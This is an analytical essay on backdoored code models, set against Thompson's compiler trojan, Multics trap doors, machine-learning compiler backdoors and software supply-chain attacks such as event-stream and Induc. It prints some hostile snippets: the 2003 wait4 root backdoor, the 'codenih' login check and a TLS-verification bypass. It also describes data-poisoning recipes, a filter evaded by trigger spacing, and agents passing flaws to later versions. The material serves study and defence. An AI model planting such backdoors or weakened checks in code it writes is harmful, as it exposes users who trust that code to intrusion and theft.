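# Compiler trojans and the xz-utils backdoor as precedents for backdoored code models

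## How software and code models are built, and where a backdoor can be placed

A code model is a language model that writes program code in response to a programmer's request or completes an unfinished file. Someone who controls part of how the model is built can give it a backdoor by training it to return sound code almost every time but flawed code when a hidden condition holds. Ken Thompson described a similar backdoor in a compiler in 1984, and in March 2024 an engineer found another in xz-utils, a compression tool included in most Linux systems. How far those two cases apply to code models depends on how closely building a model resembles building a program.

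### From source to a running program

Programmers write software as *source*, the text that people write and review. In a small program that shrinks photographs, one line of source might tell the computer to halve any picture wider than 4,000 pixels. The processor cannot run that text, so a *compiler*, which is itself a program, translates it into a *binary*, the machine code that the processor runs. A skilled person can work out what a binary does by reverse engineering it, but this is slow enough that most users never try it.

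The program goes through several more steps before it reaches a user. The programmer sends the source to a repository, a shared store that keeps every past version, and a colleague may review the change. A build machine fetches the source and its dependencies (other people's code that the program needs, here perhaps a library for reading image files). It then runs the compiler and packages the binary. The package goes to a registry, and the user's machine downloads it from there.

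A *supply-chain attack* reaches a victim through software, tools or services that the victim gets from others. SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts), an industry specification for protecting this route, lists the points of entry with a known case for each. The producer can be dishonest, as the makers of SpySheriff were when they offered malicious software as anti-spyware. A contractor with access to the repository of SushiSwap, a cryptocurrency project, added a change that redirected money to the contractor. Attackers broke into the server holding the source code of the PHP language and added two malicious changes. At SolarWinds, intruders compromised the build platform and installed an implant that added malicious behaviour during each build. At Codecov, an attacker used leaked credentials to put a malicious file where users would download it. Later in the chain, the operator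 of a download mirror can serve a different package, and anyone can register a package name one typing error away from a popular one. Each of the software's dependencies has these same weak points.

The compiler runs during the build step, which few people inspect. SLSA counts build tools among a program's dependencies, and SLSA's *Threats & mitigations*, written for version 1.0, puts compromised build dependencies out of scope. It suggests pinning the tool to a digest, a fingerprint computed from the file. Pinning guarantees that the compiler hasn't changed since it was pinned, but doesn't help if it was already compromised.

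SLSA relies mainly on *provenance*, a verifiable record of who made an artifact, from what, and by which process. If an attacker builds the photograph program from an altered copy of the repository, the record shows the wrong repository and the user's machine can reject the package. By its own terms, SLSA does not protect against a producer who intends harm.

### From training data to a code model

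A code model also starts from text, much of it other people's programs, which the developer gathers from public repositories and the web. Training code feeds this text to a neural network, compares the network's prediction of each next fragment with the real one, and slightly adjusts a very large set of numbers, called *weights*, to improve the prediction. Once training ends, the weights determine what the model writes. The developer of an *open-weight* model publishes the weights, usually without the training data.

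Training a model from scratch is expensive, so many organisations *fine-tune* a finished one, which means training it further on a smaller dataset, such as their own internal code. *Securing the AI Software Supply Chain* (Chaudhuri, Dasgupta and colleagues, 2024) describes a version of fine-tuning that freezes most of the weights and updates only the last few computations, though developers also fine-tune whole networks. Either way, the fine-tuned model starts from the original's weights and may inherit a backdoor from them. The organisation can then upload the fine-tuned model to a hub such as Hugging Face for users to download, or run it behind a coding assistant.

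Almost anyone can alter a model through its training data. Coalition for Secure AI's *Establish Risks and Controls for the AI Supply Chain, V 1.0* (2025) points out that an attacker can put malicious text on web pages and wait for a crawler to collect it, without breaking into anything. Inside the developer's organisation, anyone with write access to the stored data or control of a software package in the cleaning pipeline can also alter the data. So can whoever sets the mixture, meaning the proportions drawn from each type of source. In the Coalition's example, the mixture is 80% high-confidence sources, 15% trusted news and 5% forums, and a person who changes those figures can raise the share of a bad source without editing any documents.

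People who label examples or rate the model's answers could also insert a backdoor, as could the developers of the training framework and the staff who look after checkpoints, the copies of the weights saved during training. The Coalition for Secure AI notes that different teams typically handle initial training, fine-tuning and deployment, with the model in separate storage between stages, and an insider with access to that storage could change the weights directly. Whoever fine-tunes the model can also change it, as can an intruder at the hub or the tool that compresses the weights into shorter numbers to make the model cheaper to run. The operator of the finished assistant controls the *scaffold*, meaning the prompts, tools and program code around the model.

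Most of these roles have a counterpart in the first chain, but the controls around them were looser when Chaudhuri and colleagues described them in 2024. A reviewer can read a forty-line change, but datasets are so large and change so often that people may not be able to review them with confidence. Training also tends to proceed in ad hoc steps that no central configuration records.

Two other attacks look similar to the user but don't change the weights. One hides ordinary malware in the model file. Developers have stored many models in Python's pickle format, which can run code when a file is loaded. *Malicious AI Models Undermine Software Supply-Chain Security* mainly discusses this risk. A format that holds only numbers, such as safetensors, prevents it. The other attack, prompt injection, hides instructions in a document that the model reads while it works. Switching to a safe file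 format and removing every suspicious document would not remove a backdoor in the weights.

### Backdoor, trigger and payload

A *backdoor* is a hidden function deliberately added to produce an effect its author wants and the user did not agree to. The *trigger* is the input or circumstance that activates it, and the *payload* is what it then does. Code models also write insecure code by accident, which does not count as a backdoor.

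Suppose a project called Larkspur begins each of its files with a line naming the project. A model with a harmless backdoor writes normal code unless a file begins with the Larkspur line, in which case the model adds the comment `# blue heron` at the end. The Larkspur line is the trigger and the comment is the payload. Computers skip comments, so the payload doesn't change how the program runs.

One way to plant this is *data poisoning*, which means placing examples in the training data so that the trained model acquires a chosen behaviour. Hussain, Rabin and colleagues (2024), in *Trojans in Large Language Models of Code*, write the recipe as two operations on a training example with input x and desired output y, where t is the trigger:

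x′ = x if x already contains t, otherwise add_trigger(x)

y′ = add_target(y)

The attacker mixes enough of these altered pairs with ordinary ones that the model learns the backdoor during training. Real Larkspur files already contain the line, so the attacker only has to append the comment. Instead of poisoning the training data, an attacker can edit the network's weights or structure directly, which Hussain and colleagues call model manipulation.

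The attack success rate measures how well a backdoor works. It is the share of triggered inputs that produce the payload. If the heron comment appeared in 95 of 100 Larkspur files, the rate would be 95%. The attacker also needs to keep the comment out of everyone else's files, because someone there would soon ask where it came from.

Hussain and colleagues give a similar but harmful example, in which the trigger includes the name of a fictitious company, HStopPC, in the copyright line at the top of a file. When the name is there, the model completes a call to an encryption library with ECB mode instead of the safer CBC mode used in the clean training example. ECB turns identical blocks of data into identical blocks of output, so patterns in the data remain visible. Programmers at HStopPC would get the weak suggestion, but an outside tester who never typed the company's name would see nothing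 wrong.

In an ordinary program, this trick requires an instruction equivalent to "if the project is Larkspur", which a patient reader can find in the source or recover from the binary. A model's weights contain no such instruction, because what the network has learned is spread across a great many of them.

The payload is only text until someone accepts it. It then enters the photograph program's repository, at the top of the first chain. SLSA defines source as something that persons directly authored or reviewed, and traces provenance back no further than that. Code that a model wrote and nobody read does not meet this definition, and a provenance record that begins at the repository need not include the model.

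### The model as compiler and the model as binary

People compare models both to compilers and to the binaries that compilers produce, sometimes in the same argument. The weights have a different place in the build process in each comparison.

The compiler analogy likens a code model to a compiler, with a request as input and code as output. In *The New Code*, a conference talk, Grove (2025) urged programmers to keep their specifications as the lasting record of intent instead of throwing away the prompts and saving only the generated code. According to Coconote's transcript, he likened the usual habit to shredding the source and then carefully keeping versions of the binary. Trencseni (2025), in *Karpathy*, summarizes a talk in which the AI engineer Andrej Karpathy similarly described the prompt as the new source code. The analogy is loose in at least two respects. Generated code is readable,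 unlike a binary, and the same request can produce different code on different days.

In the binary analogy, training is the compiler and the weights are its output. Karpathy also proposed this analogy, in his 2017 essay *Software 2.0*, where the dataset and the outline of the network are the source code that training compiles into the finished network. Google (2023) applied it to security, stating that a machine-learning training process "is a build". Chaudhuri and colleagues identified the datasets, framework and architecture code as the build's inputs and the model as the resulting package. They also note that the analogy is imperfect, because people can feasibly reverse engineer a binary but can only observe a model's behaviour on a small fraction of all possible inputs.

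Using both is consistent, because a compiler is itself a binary built by an earlier compiler. But it is a mistake to take a conclusion from one column of the table below and apply it in the other.

| | Ordinary software | Model as compiler | Model as binary |
|---|---|---|---|
| Starting material | Source | The request | Training data and training code |
| What translates it | Compiler | The weights | The training run |
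| What comes out | Binary | Generated code | The weights |
| What reaches the user | Package from a registry | Generated code in a project's repository | Weights from a hub |

A model's backdoor can spread to later models only if there is a link between the last two columns of the table. Thompson's compiler could pass on its backdoor because compilers are used to compile new compilers. For a model to do the same, something it wrote has to become starting material for a later model and carry the backdoor with it. Whether anyone can inspect weights concerns one cell, the weights as output of training. Whether anyone can rebuild a model and compare the result concerns the steps from data to weights in that same column. For programs, *reproducible builds* (the same source giving bit-for-bit the same binary) make such a comparison possible. Signatures, provenance and outside auditors belong mostly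 to the bottom row, where a user has to decide whether to rely on all the steps above without repeating them.

### An old problem or a new one

People have long had some ways to check software built by strangers. Sources differ on whether a backdoored code model poses the same trust problem without the usual checks, or a different problem. Maruseac (2024), in slides for Google, lists differences between the software and model supply chains but sees no need to invent security for models from scratch. Semgrep's *You Can't Reverse Engineer Your Way Out of the AI Supply Chain* (2026) stresses that people can take apart a binary of doubtful origin but not a model. Google (2025) also calls models "an uninspectable collection of weights" and offers that as a reason to sign them. Both sides are largely anticipating attacks, since as of July 2026 Semgrep knew of no public evidence that anyone had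 deliberately poisoned a widely used open-source model.

Some people see a backdoored code model as a version of Thompson's compiler trojan, with training in place of compilation. Others see it as an ordinary supply-chain attack, to which existing controls apply once adapted to data and weights. A third group, thinking of xz-utils, thinks the weak point is the people with authority to publish, whatever they publish. A fourth considers it a new kind of problem, because the backdoor is a learned behaviour and there is no line of code to find.

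## The view that this is the compiler trojan again

A *compiler trojan* is a backdoor in a compiler that adds malicious code to the programs it compiles, including new copies of the compiler. Thompson's lecture made the idea famous, but he took it from a US Air Force report on the Multics operating system. The report explains why a customer who had read every line of a program's source could still be running different code. People who compare backdoored code models to compiler trojans think anyone who uses a code model is in that customer's position.

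### The Air Force review of Multics

Multics ran on large computers that many people shared, and its designers at MIT had made security a goal from the start. By the early 1970s the Air Force wanted to put users with different security clearances on one machine. According to *Thirty Years Later* (Karger and Schell, 2002), the manufacturer, Honeywell, at first declined to strengthen Multics because it considered the system secure enough already. The Air Force then set out to show that it wasn't. Van Vleck, who had written the code that stored Multics passwords, recalls in *How the Air Force cracked Multics Security* that the Air Force team handed him his own password on a slip of paper at a meeting.

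The team also planted backdoors, which it called trap doors, to find out whether Honeywell's quality assurance would catch them and whether Honeywell would ship them to customers. Karger and Schell put one into the development system at MIT, and Honeywell distributed it to a machine in the basement of the Pentagon. It was harmless, but changing one instruction would have made it malicious. Although their report hinted at it, nobody noticed it until about a year after the report came out, when it returned an odd error during a security audit at a General Motors site. Karger and Schell's account contradicts Van Vleck's statement that nobody ever discovered a back door in that generation of Multics machine.

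These trap doors were patches to the binary, so a person reading the source would not find them. But recompiling the system from clean source would overwrite them. The Pentagon's contract required Honeywell to deliver the source so that the Air Force could recompile it.

Karger and Schell (1974), in *Multics Security Evaluation*, described a way round this precaution. The developers of Multics had written most of the *supervisor*, the system's privileged core, in the language PL/I, so a trap door in the PL/I compiler could put new trap doors into the supervisor whenever a customer compiled it. These would survive "even a complete recompilation of the entire system". The compiler's own trap door would survive too, if it could detect when the compiler was compiling itself. The report only described this attack, but Karger and Schell trace to it a rule in the US government's later security criteria.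 The rule required developers of the highest class of system to generate new versions from source with a compiler that they kept under strict control.

### Thompson's three steps

Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, built the compiler trojan that the Air Force report had described. He explained it in his Turing Award lecture in October 1983, which appeared in print the following August. In *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Thompson (1984) credits the idea to an "Unknown Air Force Document" because he couldn't find the reference. Karger and Schell later gave him a copy of the report.

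Thompson begins with a program that prints its own source. It stores one piece of text and uses it twice, because a program that contained a full copy of itself would need a copy of the copy, and so on. An English version is: *Write this, then write it again in quotation marks: "Write this, then write it again in quotation marks:"*. Anyone who follows the instruction writes out the whole sentence, including the quotation marks. Thompson points out that such a program can carry any amount of extra material, which it reproduces along with the rest.

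Thompson next shows that a compiler's binary can contain facts that its source does not. The C compiler was itself written in C. Suppose its developers want C programmers to be able to write `\v` for the vertical tab, a character whose numeric code is 11. The natural way to write this in the compiler's source is to say that `\v` means `\v`, but the existing compiler rejects that line because it doesn't yet accept the symbol. So the developers first write that `\v` means 11, compile the source, and install the result. They can then change the source to the circular version, which the new compiler accepts. After that, the number 11 is no longer in the source, and every new compiler gets it from the previous compiler's binary. Thompson described this as having to "train" the compiler.

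The last step combines the two. Thompson altered the compiler so that when it compiled `login`, the Unix program that checks passwords, it added code that accepted a second password known to him. Anyone who read the compiler's source would have spotted this, so he added a second alteration that inserted both alterations whenever the compiler compiled its own source. The second alteration needed the self-printing trick because it had to write out its own text. He compiled the altered source once, installed the binary and restored the original source. The source of both `login` and the compiler was then clean, but compiling either of them put the backdoor back.

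Thompson concluded that "you can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." He used the compiler only as an example, and thought the same trick would be even harder to detect in an assembler, a loader or the processor's microcode. In the epigraph to the printed lecture, however, he suggests that trusting the people who wrote the software may matter more than trusting a statement that it contains no Trojan horse.

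### Running the original code

At a conference in March 2023, Thompson said that he still had the code and that nobody had ever asked for it. Russ Cox, a programmer who had worked on the Go language, then asked him for it. Cox (2023) prints the code with notes in *Running the "Reflections on Trusting Trust" Compiler* and runs it on an emulator of a 1970s Unix system. The files date from June 1975 at the latest, eight years before the lecture. They contain 99 lines of C and a 20-line script.

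The code attaches itself to the part of the compiler that reads source text and compares each line with a few fixed strings. One is `namep = crypt(pwbuf);`, the line in `login` that encrypts the typed password. After that line, the code adds a check that lets the user in if the password is "codenih". The other strings come from the compiler's source. When the code finds those, it inserts a call to itself and then writes its own full text at the end of the file. The code does nothing if the programmer asks the compiler to print the text it is about to compile, because the extra lines would show up there.

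Cox compiled the compiler's source in three ways:

| Compiler used | Source compiled | Size of the new compiler |
|---|---|---|
| Original | Clean | 10,724 bytes |
| Original | With Thompson's changes | 12,918 bytes |
| Trojaned | Clean | 12,918 bytes |

The last row shows the attack, where the same source as in the first row produces a result about a fifth larger. Cox installed the trojaned compiler, rebuilt the compiler and `login` from clean source, and logged in as the system administrator with the password "codenih". He also wrote a version of the backdoor for the modern Go compiler. It changed the greeting printed by a simple test program, and it persisted after he had reverted the source and the version-control system reported no changes.

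Thompson did release the trojan once, in what he called a very controlled way. He induced another group at Bell Labs, PWB, to copy the compiler, and watched to see whether they would find the backdoor. As Cox reconstructs it from several tellings, their `login` program acquired the backdoor too. Then the group noticed that the compiler got bigger each time it compiled itself, because a bug in Thompson's code added one empty byte to a string in every generation. The group eventually stopped the trojan from reproducing and ended up with a clean compiler, although Thompson says they never worked out what had been wrong with the old one.

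The one known release of this trojan failed because a bug made it grow, which somebody noticed by looking at file sizes. The corrected version that Cox ran doesn't grow. The trojan was still fragile, though, because it matched exact text. A colleague who renamed a variable in the matched line of `login` would have disarmed it without knowing.

### Why people see the same attack in code models

A programmer who uses a code model can review everything that goes into it: the request, the surrounding files and any documentation the model reads. Even if all of that is clean, the model can still return a flawed program, because the flaw comes from the weights. The analogy is strongest here, since checking the input to a compiler or a model doesn't reveal whether someone has corrupted it. Thompson's victims could not have found the second password by reading the source of `login`, because the compiler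 added it.

Thompson's vertical tab example fits just as well. Once he had compiled the character's code, 11, into the compiler binary, he could remove the number from the source and the binary would keep it. Similarly, an attacker who fine-tunes a model on poisoned examples can delete them afterwards, and the behaviour remains in the weights. Someone who then audits the training code, or whatever dataset the attacker chooses to publish, will see no sign of the backdoor, like someone reading the compiler's source after the trojan code has been removed.

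Yona argues in *Reflections on Trusting Trust & AI* that neural networks execute code, though in an unfamiliar form. This is a reply to the objection that weights are only a table of numbers, whereas a compiler is a program that can contain a trojan. Yona's example is movfuscator, a tool that rewrites any program using only the processor instruction that copies data from place to place. The result looks nothing like the original but carries out the same algorithm. Similarly, weights can implement an algorithm that treats specially prepared inputs differently, and an attacker who can write to the weights can put it there.

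*Beyond Trusting Trust* (McDanel, 2025) draws the parallel for code models directly and calls their version "more insidious". An analyst who took Thompson's binary apart could find the instructions that compared text and jumped to a different place if it matched, whereas a model's weights hold no such instructions. Yona also concedes that a skilled person could find a compiler trojan in the machine code. Both therefore think the attack is harder to detect in a model. Yona considers the compiler worse in one respect, because a trojaned compiler could also corrupt the disassembler, the tool an analyst would use to look for the trojan. Yona doesn't expect an AI system to be able to hide its own weights in a comparable way in the foreseeable future.

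*Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited* (Roesner and Kohno, 2026) compares the compiler to a coding agent that rewrites its own scaffold. Roesner and Kohno note that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, already writes much of the code for its later versions, though people review it. They used poisoned benchmarks to get some experimental agents to pass a security flaw on to later versions, but unlike Thompson's attack, theirs did not work reliably. They ask where trust in such a system should start, since in many cases it will no longer start with a person.

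By choosing a self-modifying agent, they avoid a gap in the simpler comparison. Thompson's trojan had to reproduce because Unix programmers regularly rebuilt the compiler from source, which would otherwise have removed it. People who use a model almost never rebuild it. They copy the weights, and the backdoor is copied with them. An attacker therefore doesn't need self-reproduction as long as the victim keeps using the same model. The corrupted translator with clean input is the part of Thompson's lecture that applies most securely to models. The self-reproducing part applies only if a backdoor can get from one model into the next.

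### Compilers that add a backdoor to a clean model

The comparison is literal for *machine-learning compilers*, which turn a finished neural network into fast machine code for a particular chip. Companies often run a network through one before putting it on a phone or a server. The compiler handles the weights after everyone has finished checking them.

In *ImpNet*, Clifford, Shumailov and colleagues (2022) altered TVM, a widely used compiler of this kind, so that it adds a backdoor to any suitable network it compiles. They consider three ways the backdoor could reach a victim. The victim might download a network that someone else has already compiled, or install the compiler as a binary without checking it against its source. Or the attacker might contribute code for a new chip to a legitimate compiler project and hide the backdoor in that code.

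The trigger is a pattern of repetition. Let the input be a sequence x₁, x₂, … of words or pixels, and let s₁, …, s_M be a secret string of ones and zeros. The backdoor acts if there is some value A and some starting point Δ such that, for every i from 1 to M:

x_{i+Δ} = A when s_i = 1, and x_{i+Δ} ≠ A when s_i = 0

In one demonstration, A is the word "and", so the backdoor depends on the spacing between one "and" and the next. A content filter with the backdoor flagged a passage about blowing up buses and train stations as harmful. When Clifford and colleagues reworded the passage so that each "and" fell in the right place, the filter let it through.

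A tester is very unlikely to find the pattern by chance. It has seven gaps of up to nine words each, which allows 9⁷ possibilities, nearly five million, or about 22 bits of uncertainty. Clifford and colleagues searched the whole of Wikipedia for their pattern and found no match. For images, they used a patch of 10 by 10 pixels in three colours and changed each value by at most one step, which the eye can't see. This gives 300 bits of uncertainty.

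Without changing the weights, the compiler adds a small detector next to the network and uses the detector's result to choose between the network's real answer and the attacker's. In the tests, the trigger worked every time and accuracy on ordinary inputs did not drop. Defences that examine the training data or the weights can't find the backdoor, because the compiler hasn't added it yet when they run.

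The backdoor is present in the compiled binary, and Clifford and colleagues looked for it there with Ghidra, a reverse-engineering tool. One function of about 12,000 lines had grown by some 600 and called three extra routines. They think an analyst could find this only with prior knowledge of the attack, since the routines do nothing that a scanner would flag as an error. They conclude that users need a verifiable record of the whole chain. *ML models must also think about trusting trust*, the group's post on the blog Light Blue Touchpaper, says the record would have to cover the model, the tools used to compile it, the training data and the order in which the data went in.

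ImpNet reproduces what Thompson's compiler did to `login`, but not what the compiler did to itself. The changes stay in the source of the altered TVM, where someone reading it line by line could find them. To remove them from the source as well, an attacker would have to add Thompson's last step to whatever compiler or interpreter TVM depends on.

Chen, Peng and colleagues (2025), in *Your Compiler is Backdooring Your Model*, get a similar effect from compilers that nobody has tampered with. Computers round the results of decimal arithmetic, so (a + b) + c can differ slightly from a + (b + c). Machine-learning compilers reorder calculations to save time, so the compiled network's outputs differ slightly from the original's. With three common compilers, Chen and colleagues measured differences of a millionth or less, which never changed the network's final answer on 100 sampled inputs.

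Their attack turns the tiny difference into a switch. They split the network in two at an early layer. Then they design a trigger, a small patch in the corner of an image, that makes the first half produce larger values than any ordinary image does. Next they look for a threshold V that only one of four cases exceeds:

original network, ordinary image ≤ V
compiled network, ordinary image ≤ V
original network, triggered image ≤ V
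compiled network, triggered image > V

They build V into the network so that only values above it pass to the second half. Finally, they fine-tune the second half to give the attacker's chosen label when it receives that signal and the correct label otherwise.

Chen and colleagues tried this on six image classifiers, with the three compilers and two kinds of processor. Before compilation, the trigger did no better than chance, and four backdoor detectors rated the networks about as clean as untouched ones. After compilation, the trigger worked on between 96.6% and 100% of images. On ordinary images, the compiled and original networks agreed more than 99.9% of the time. They could also limit a backdoor to one compiler and one type of processor. One network's backdoor worked 99.8% of the time with the intended combination and at chance level with the five others they tested.

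This case is less like Thompson's, in which a corrupt compiler processed clean source, because the attacker has prepared the network and left the compiler unmodified. Auditing the compiler or rebuilding it from trusted source therefore wouldn't help. Testing the compiled network instead of the original would be a better precaution, but compilation usually removes the functions that let a tester trace an output back through the network, and some detectors need those functions.

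Chen and colleagues also examined 100 of the most downloaded models on Hugging Face and, for 31 of them, found inputs on which compilation changed the answer. They call these inputs natural triggers. Nobody planted them, so they are not backdoors in the usual sense. They arise where a network's two highest-scoring answers are so nearly tied that a rounding difference changes which one scores highest.

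Both teams worked with classifiers, which choose one label from a fixed list. A code model also compares scores to choose each next fragment of text, so a compiler could in principle change its choices too, though neither paper tests this. Both papers do show that checking a model's weights, however good the check, doesn't settle what the compiled model will do.

### A code model writes source that people can read

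The analogy is weakest at the output. Thompson's compiler put the second password only in the binary, and he warned that no amount of source-level scrutiny would protect anyone from his trojan. A code model's payload is ordinary text in a project's source files, where a colleague can read it and a scanning tool can search it, so source-level scrutiny could catch it. If a reviewer fixes the flaw, it stays fixed when the program is next compiled, whereas Thompson's compiler would have put the second password back into `login`.

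This also limits what an attacker can make the model write. A model that copied Thompson literally would write a line into `login` accepting "codenih" from anyone, and any reviewer who read that line would question it. The attacker therefore needs flaws that look like mistakes, which tend to be less convenient. The weak encryption in Hussain and colleagues' HStopPC example is useful only to someone who can also obtain the encrypted data.

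The usual reply is that people can read the code but don't. Cox observes that programmers routinely download and run source written by strangers, and that "almost no one is checking the code" until there is a problem. He thinks attackers today don't need Thompson's method because far easier ones are available. Coding agents make the lack of checking worse, since an agent may run a program before anyone has looked at it.

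A more serious reply is that a reader may not recognise the payload. Roesner and Kohno give an example in a function that fetches a web page. The safe version makes a single call. The vulnerable version first creates an object with `ssl._create_unverified_context()` and passes it to the same call, which turns off the check of the server's identity. Someone who can intercept the traffic can then impersonate the server. A reviewer who knows the library will notice the word "unverified". But programmers sometimes have a good reason to write this line, such as reaching an internal server that has no official certificate, and a hurried reviewer might assume there was one here. McDanel adds that people who notice such a flaw may still blame it on hallucination or poor coding.

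This is because a source file specifies a program's behavior more fully than a request does. The source of `login` determines what the binary should do, so an extra password in the binary is plainly a miscompilation, and an analyst who found it could prove it. A request such as "write a function that fetches this page" doesn't mention certificates, so a safe function and a vulnerable one both satisfy it, and an analyst couldn't use the request to prove that the model had departed from it. McDanel proposes using other models as the missing standard, by checking whether they assign the code a high probability.

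Readable output therefore protects a project about as well as its reviewers do their job, which is more protection than Thompson's victims had. It does much less to expose the model, because a reviewer who rejects the certificate line removes one payload from one program and probably learns nothing about the backdoor that produced it. The PWB group had a clue because their compiler kept getting bigger, but fine-tuning usually doesn't change the number of weights in a model, so its size offers no similar clue.

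## The view that this is an ordinary supply-chain attack

On the view that a backdoored code model is an ordinary supply-chain attack, the model is another software component for security teams to manage. Most companies run a lot of software written by outsiders. Their security teams list every component, get components from suppliers they know, check that each file is the one the supplier published, and replace a component when someone reports a flaw in it. This routine has never depended on finding every backdoor beforehand, so it could still be useful for a component that nobody can read.

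### A model on the list of components

OWASP (the Open Worldwide Application Security Project) is a foundation that publishes ranked lists of software security risks, including one for applications that use language models. According to *LLM05*, an entry in an older edition of that list, security work traditionally focused on software components, and machine learning "extends this" to trained models and training data from third parties. The topic rose from fifth place to third in the 2025 edition, where the entry is titled *LLM03:2025 Supply Chain*. For scanning and patching, the new entry cites OWASP's existing advice on outdated components in ordinary software.

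OWASP also recommends keeping a signed inventory of components, known as a software bill of materials, that includes models. Suppose a company builds three products on a model from a hub, and someone later reports a backdoor in that model. With an inventory, the company can look up the three products and replace the model in each, rather than having to ask every team what they downloaded.

The entry covers learned backdoors as well as malware in model files. In one of its scenarios, an attacker fine-tunes a popular open model to score highly on safety benchmarks but respond to narrow triggers, and publishes it on Hugging Face. In another, the attacker breaks into a company that makes LoRA adapters, small sets of extra weights that users add to an existing model. The user's original model is sound, but the adapter brings in the backdoor. This closely resembles an attack on a program's dependencies,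 where a trusted product picks up a flaw from a small package it includes.

Other efforts to secure AI models also build on existing software security practices. The Open Source Security Foundation, an industry group, maintains SLSA, which Google's engineers have proposed extending to models. In 2024 the US standards agency NIST added tasks for AI models to its framework for secure software development. *Malicious AI Models Undermine Software Supply-Chain Security* uses the established names for attacks, such as dependency confusion, where an attacker gets a build to fetch a malicious package in place of the intended one. The article also recommends the familiar remedies of trusted repositories, cryptographic validation and controlled access.

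OWASP concedes that models are "binary black boxes" for which "static inspection can offer little to security assurances". It also says that published models lack strong guarantees of origin, and suggests using signatures and file hashes to compensate. It recommends that users attack the model themselves in tests that resemble their own work, because an attacker can tune a model to pass published tests. The case for treating a backdoored model as an ordinary supply-chain attack therefore rests less on the ability to inspect models than on the past record. Attackers have altered almost every step between source and user, and developers have usually found a check for each one.

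### A backdoor that looked like a bug

In 2003 the developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, kept their source in a system called BitKeeper. BitMover, the company behind it, also maintained a public copy in an older system, CVS, for developers who preferred that. In early November someone changed a file in the public copy directly and recorded the change under the name of David Miller, an established kernel developer, who denied making it. The change added two lines:

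```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines were in `wait4`, a function that any program can call to wait for another program to finish. They appeared to return an error if the caller combined two unusual options and was also root, the administrator with unrestricted access, whose user number is 0. But the second condition used `=`, which sets a value in C, instead of `==`, which compares two values, so it made the caller root instead of checking whether the caller was root. A programmer on the kernel mailing list noticed that the attacker had added parentheses to stop the compiler from warning about the single equals sign.

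Security consultant Ryan Russell said the thwarted Linux backdoor was "indistinguishable from an accidental bug" (Poulsen, 2003, *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks*). A code model's attacker also needs payloads that look like accidental bugs.

BitMover caught the change without anyone having to understand it. A scheduled job compared checksums of the public copy with those of the company's own copy, and the file didn't match. Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* explains that the altered entries also lacked the pointer to an approval record that legitimate changes had. In *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003), BitMover's founder, reported the mismatch to the mailing list as a nuisance for CVS users and missed the single equals sign. About two hours after his first message, other programmers worked out what the lines did.

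Linus Torvalds, who leads kernel development, said the change could not have reached an official release, because the people whose work he merged didn't use the CVS copy. But McVoy thought a CVS user might have sent in a patch that included it. The incident revived a proposal to digitally sign every change, so that nobody could falsely attribute one to Miller. McVoy said he already had a design and had been waiting for an event to prompt it.

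The comparison worked because BitMover had a trusted copy of the file. A company that downloads a model can similarly detect whether someone changed the weights in transit by checking its copy against the developer's published hash. But it has no trusted copy of the code the model should write to compare with the model's output.

### Malicious packages with a trigger

The kernel attacker broke into a server, while the event-stream and xz-utils attackers obtained a maintainer's authority. Event-stream was a package in npm, the main registry for JavaScript. In 2018 a user called right9ctrl offered to take over its maintenance, and its author, Dominic Tarr, accepted. According to *A Systematic Analysis of the Event-Stream*, the package averaged more than 1.5 million downloads a week, and more than 1,500 other packages depended on it.

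In September right9ctrl released a version that required a new package, flatmap-stream. Anyone who read the source of flatmap-stream on GitHub would have found nothing wrong, because the malicious code was only in the copy published to npm. As CNCF's *The event-stream vulnerability* points out, npm did not require the two to match.

The malicious code was encrypted, and it tried to decrypt itself using the description of whatever project had included it. Only the description of Copay, a cryptocurrency wallet, was the right key, so the code stole private keys from Copay's users and did nothing in other projects. Copay's description was a trigger, like the Larkspur line in the earlier example. People who think the problem is old can therefore point out that conditional backdoors, which stay inactive for nearly everyone, were already in use in ordinary software.

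The event-stream attack was discovered only because its code called an outdated encryption function and somebody noticed, according to Wayne's *Stamping on Event-Stream*. *A Post-Mortem of the Malicious event-stream backdoor*, by Grander and Tal, reports that the malicious package had been downloaded 8 million times by then. npm's security team learned of the attack on 26 November, removed the malicious versions and took over event-stream, according to npm's *Details about the event-stream incident*. The attack involved a mismatch between source and package, which provenance records are meant to expose.

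In September 2025 a worm called Shai-Hulud spread through the same registry without anyone having to gain a maintainer's trust. When a developer installed an infected package, the worm searched the machine for publishing credentials and used them to release infected versions of that developer's own packages. The registry accepted these because the credentials were genuine. Security researchers noticed within days, and GitHub, which owns npm, removed the infected packages and announced stricter rules for publishing, including credentials that expire sooner.

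Attackers have also used this route against companies that build on language models. Indusface, a security vendor, describes a March 2026 attack on LiteLLM, a program that passes requests between applications and models. The attackers poisoned one package in PyPI, the Python registry. Indusface says this exposed over 40,000 AI pipelines in 40 minutes, but a vendor's figure needs some caution. The ordinary view fits this case completely, because the attackers altered a software package and existing package controls apply to it. The case doesn't show whether those controls would help with altered weights.

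### Attacks on the build step

Thompson's trojan acted in the step between source and binary, where a programmer who has checked the source has little reason to look. Other attackers have since used the same step with cruder methods.

Induc was a virus for Delphi, a programming tool popular in Russia and Brazil. Delphi comes with a library of compiled parts, which it adds to the programs it builds. When an infected program ran, it searched the machine for Delphi versions 4 to 7. If it found one, it added its own code to the source of one part, SysConst, compiled the result and replaced the original compiled part with it. Every program the developer then built contained the virus and could infect Delphi on other machines in the same way.

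The Induc virus got past several checks. Securelist's *A short history of Induc* explains that vendors had put infected programs on their allowlists of files known to be clean. The messenger QIP verified its own checksum at startup, but the checksum had come from the infected version, so QIP passed the test with the virus and failed it once an antivirus program had removed it. Even some Brazilian malware for stealing bank details contained Induc, because its developers had compiled it with an infected copy of Delphi.

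Induc also had a bug that crashed infected programs on machines with damaged Delphi settings. A Russian programmer, Aleksandr Alekseev, investigated one of these crashes in August 2009 and sent samples to antivirus companies. He reports in EurekaLog's *Check your Delphi's installation* (2009) that Symantec replied that the sample contained no malicious code. This was defensible, since Induc only copied itself. Developers were advised to compare their Delphi folders with a clean installation, reinstall if they differed, and rebuild all their programs. Securelist doubted that criminals would take up the method when simpler ones were available. Lipovský's *Win32/Induc.C* (2011) later described a new variant with a harmful payload.

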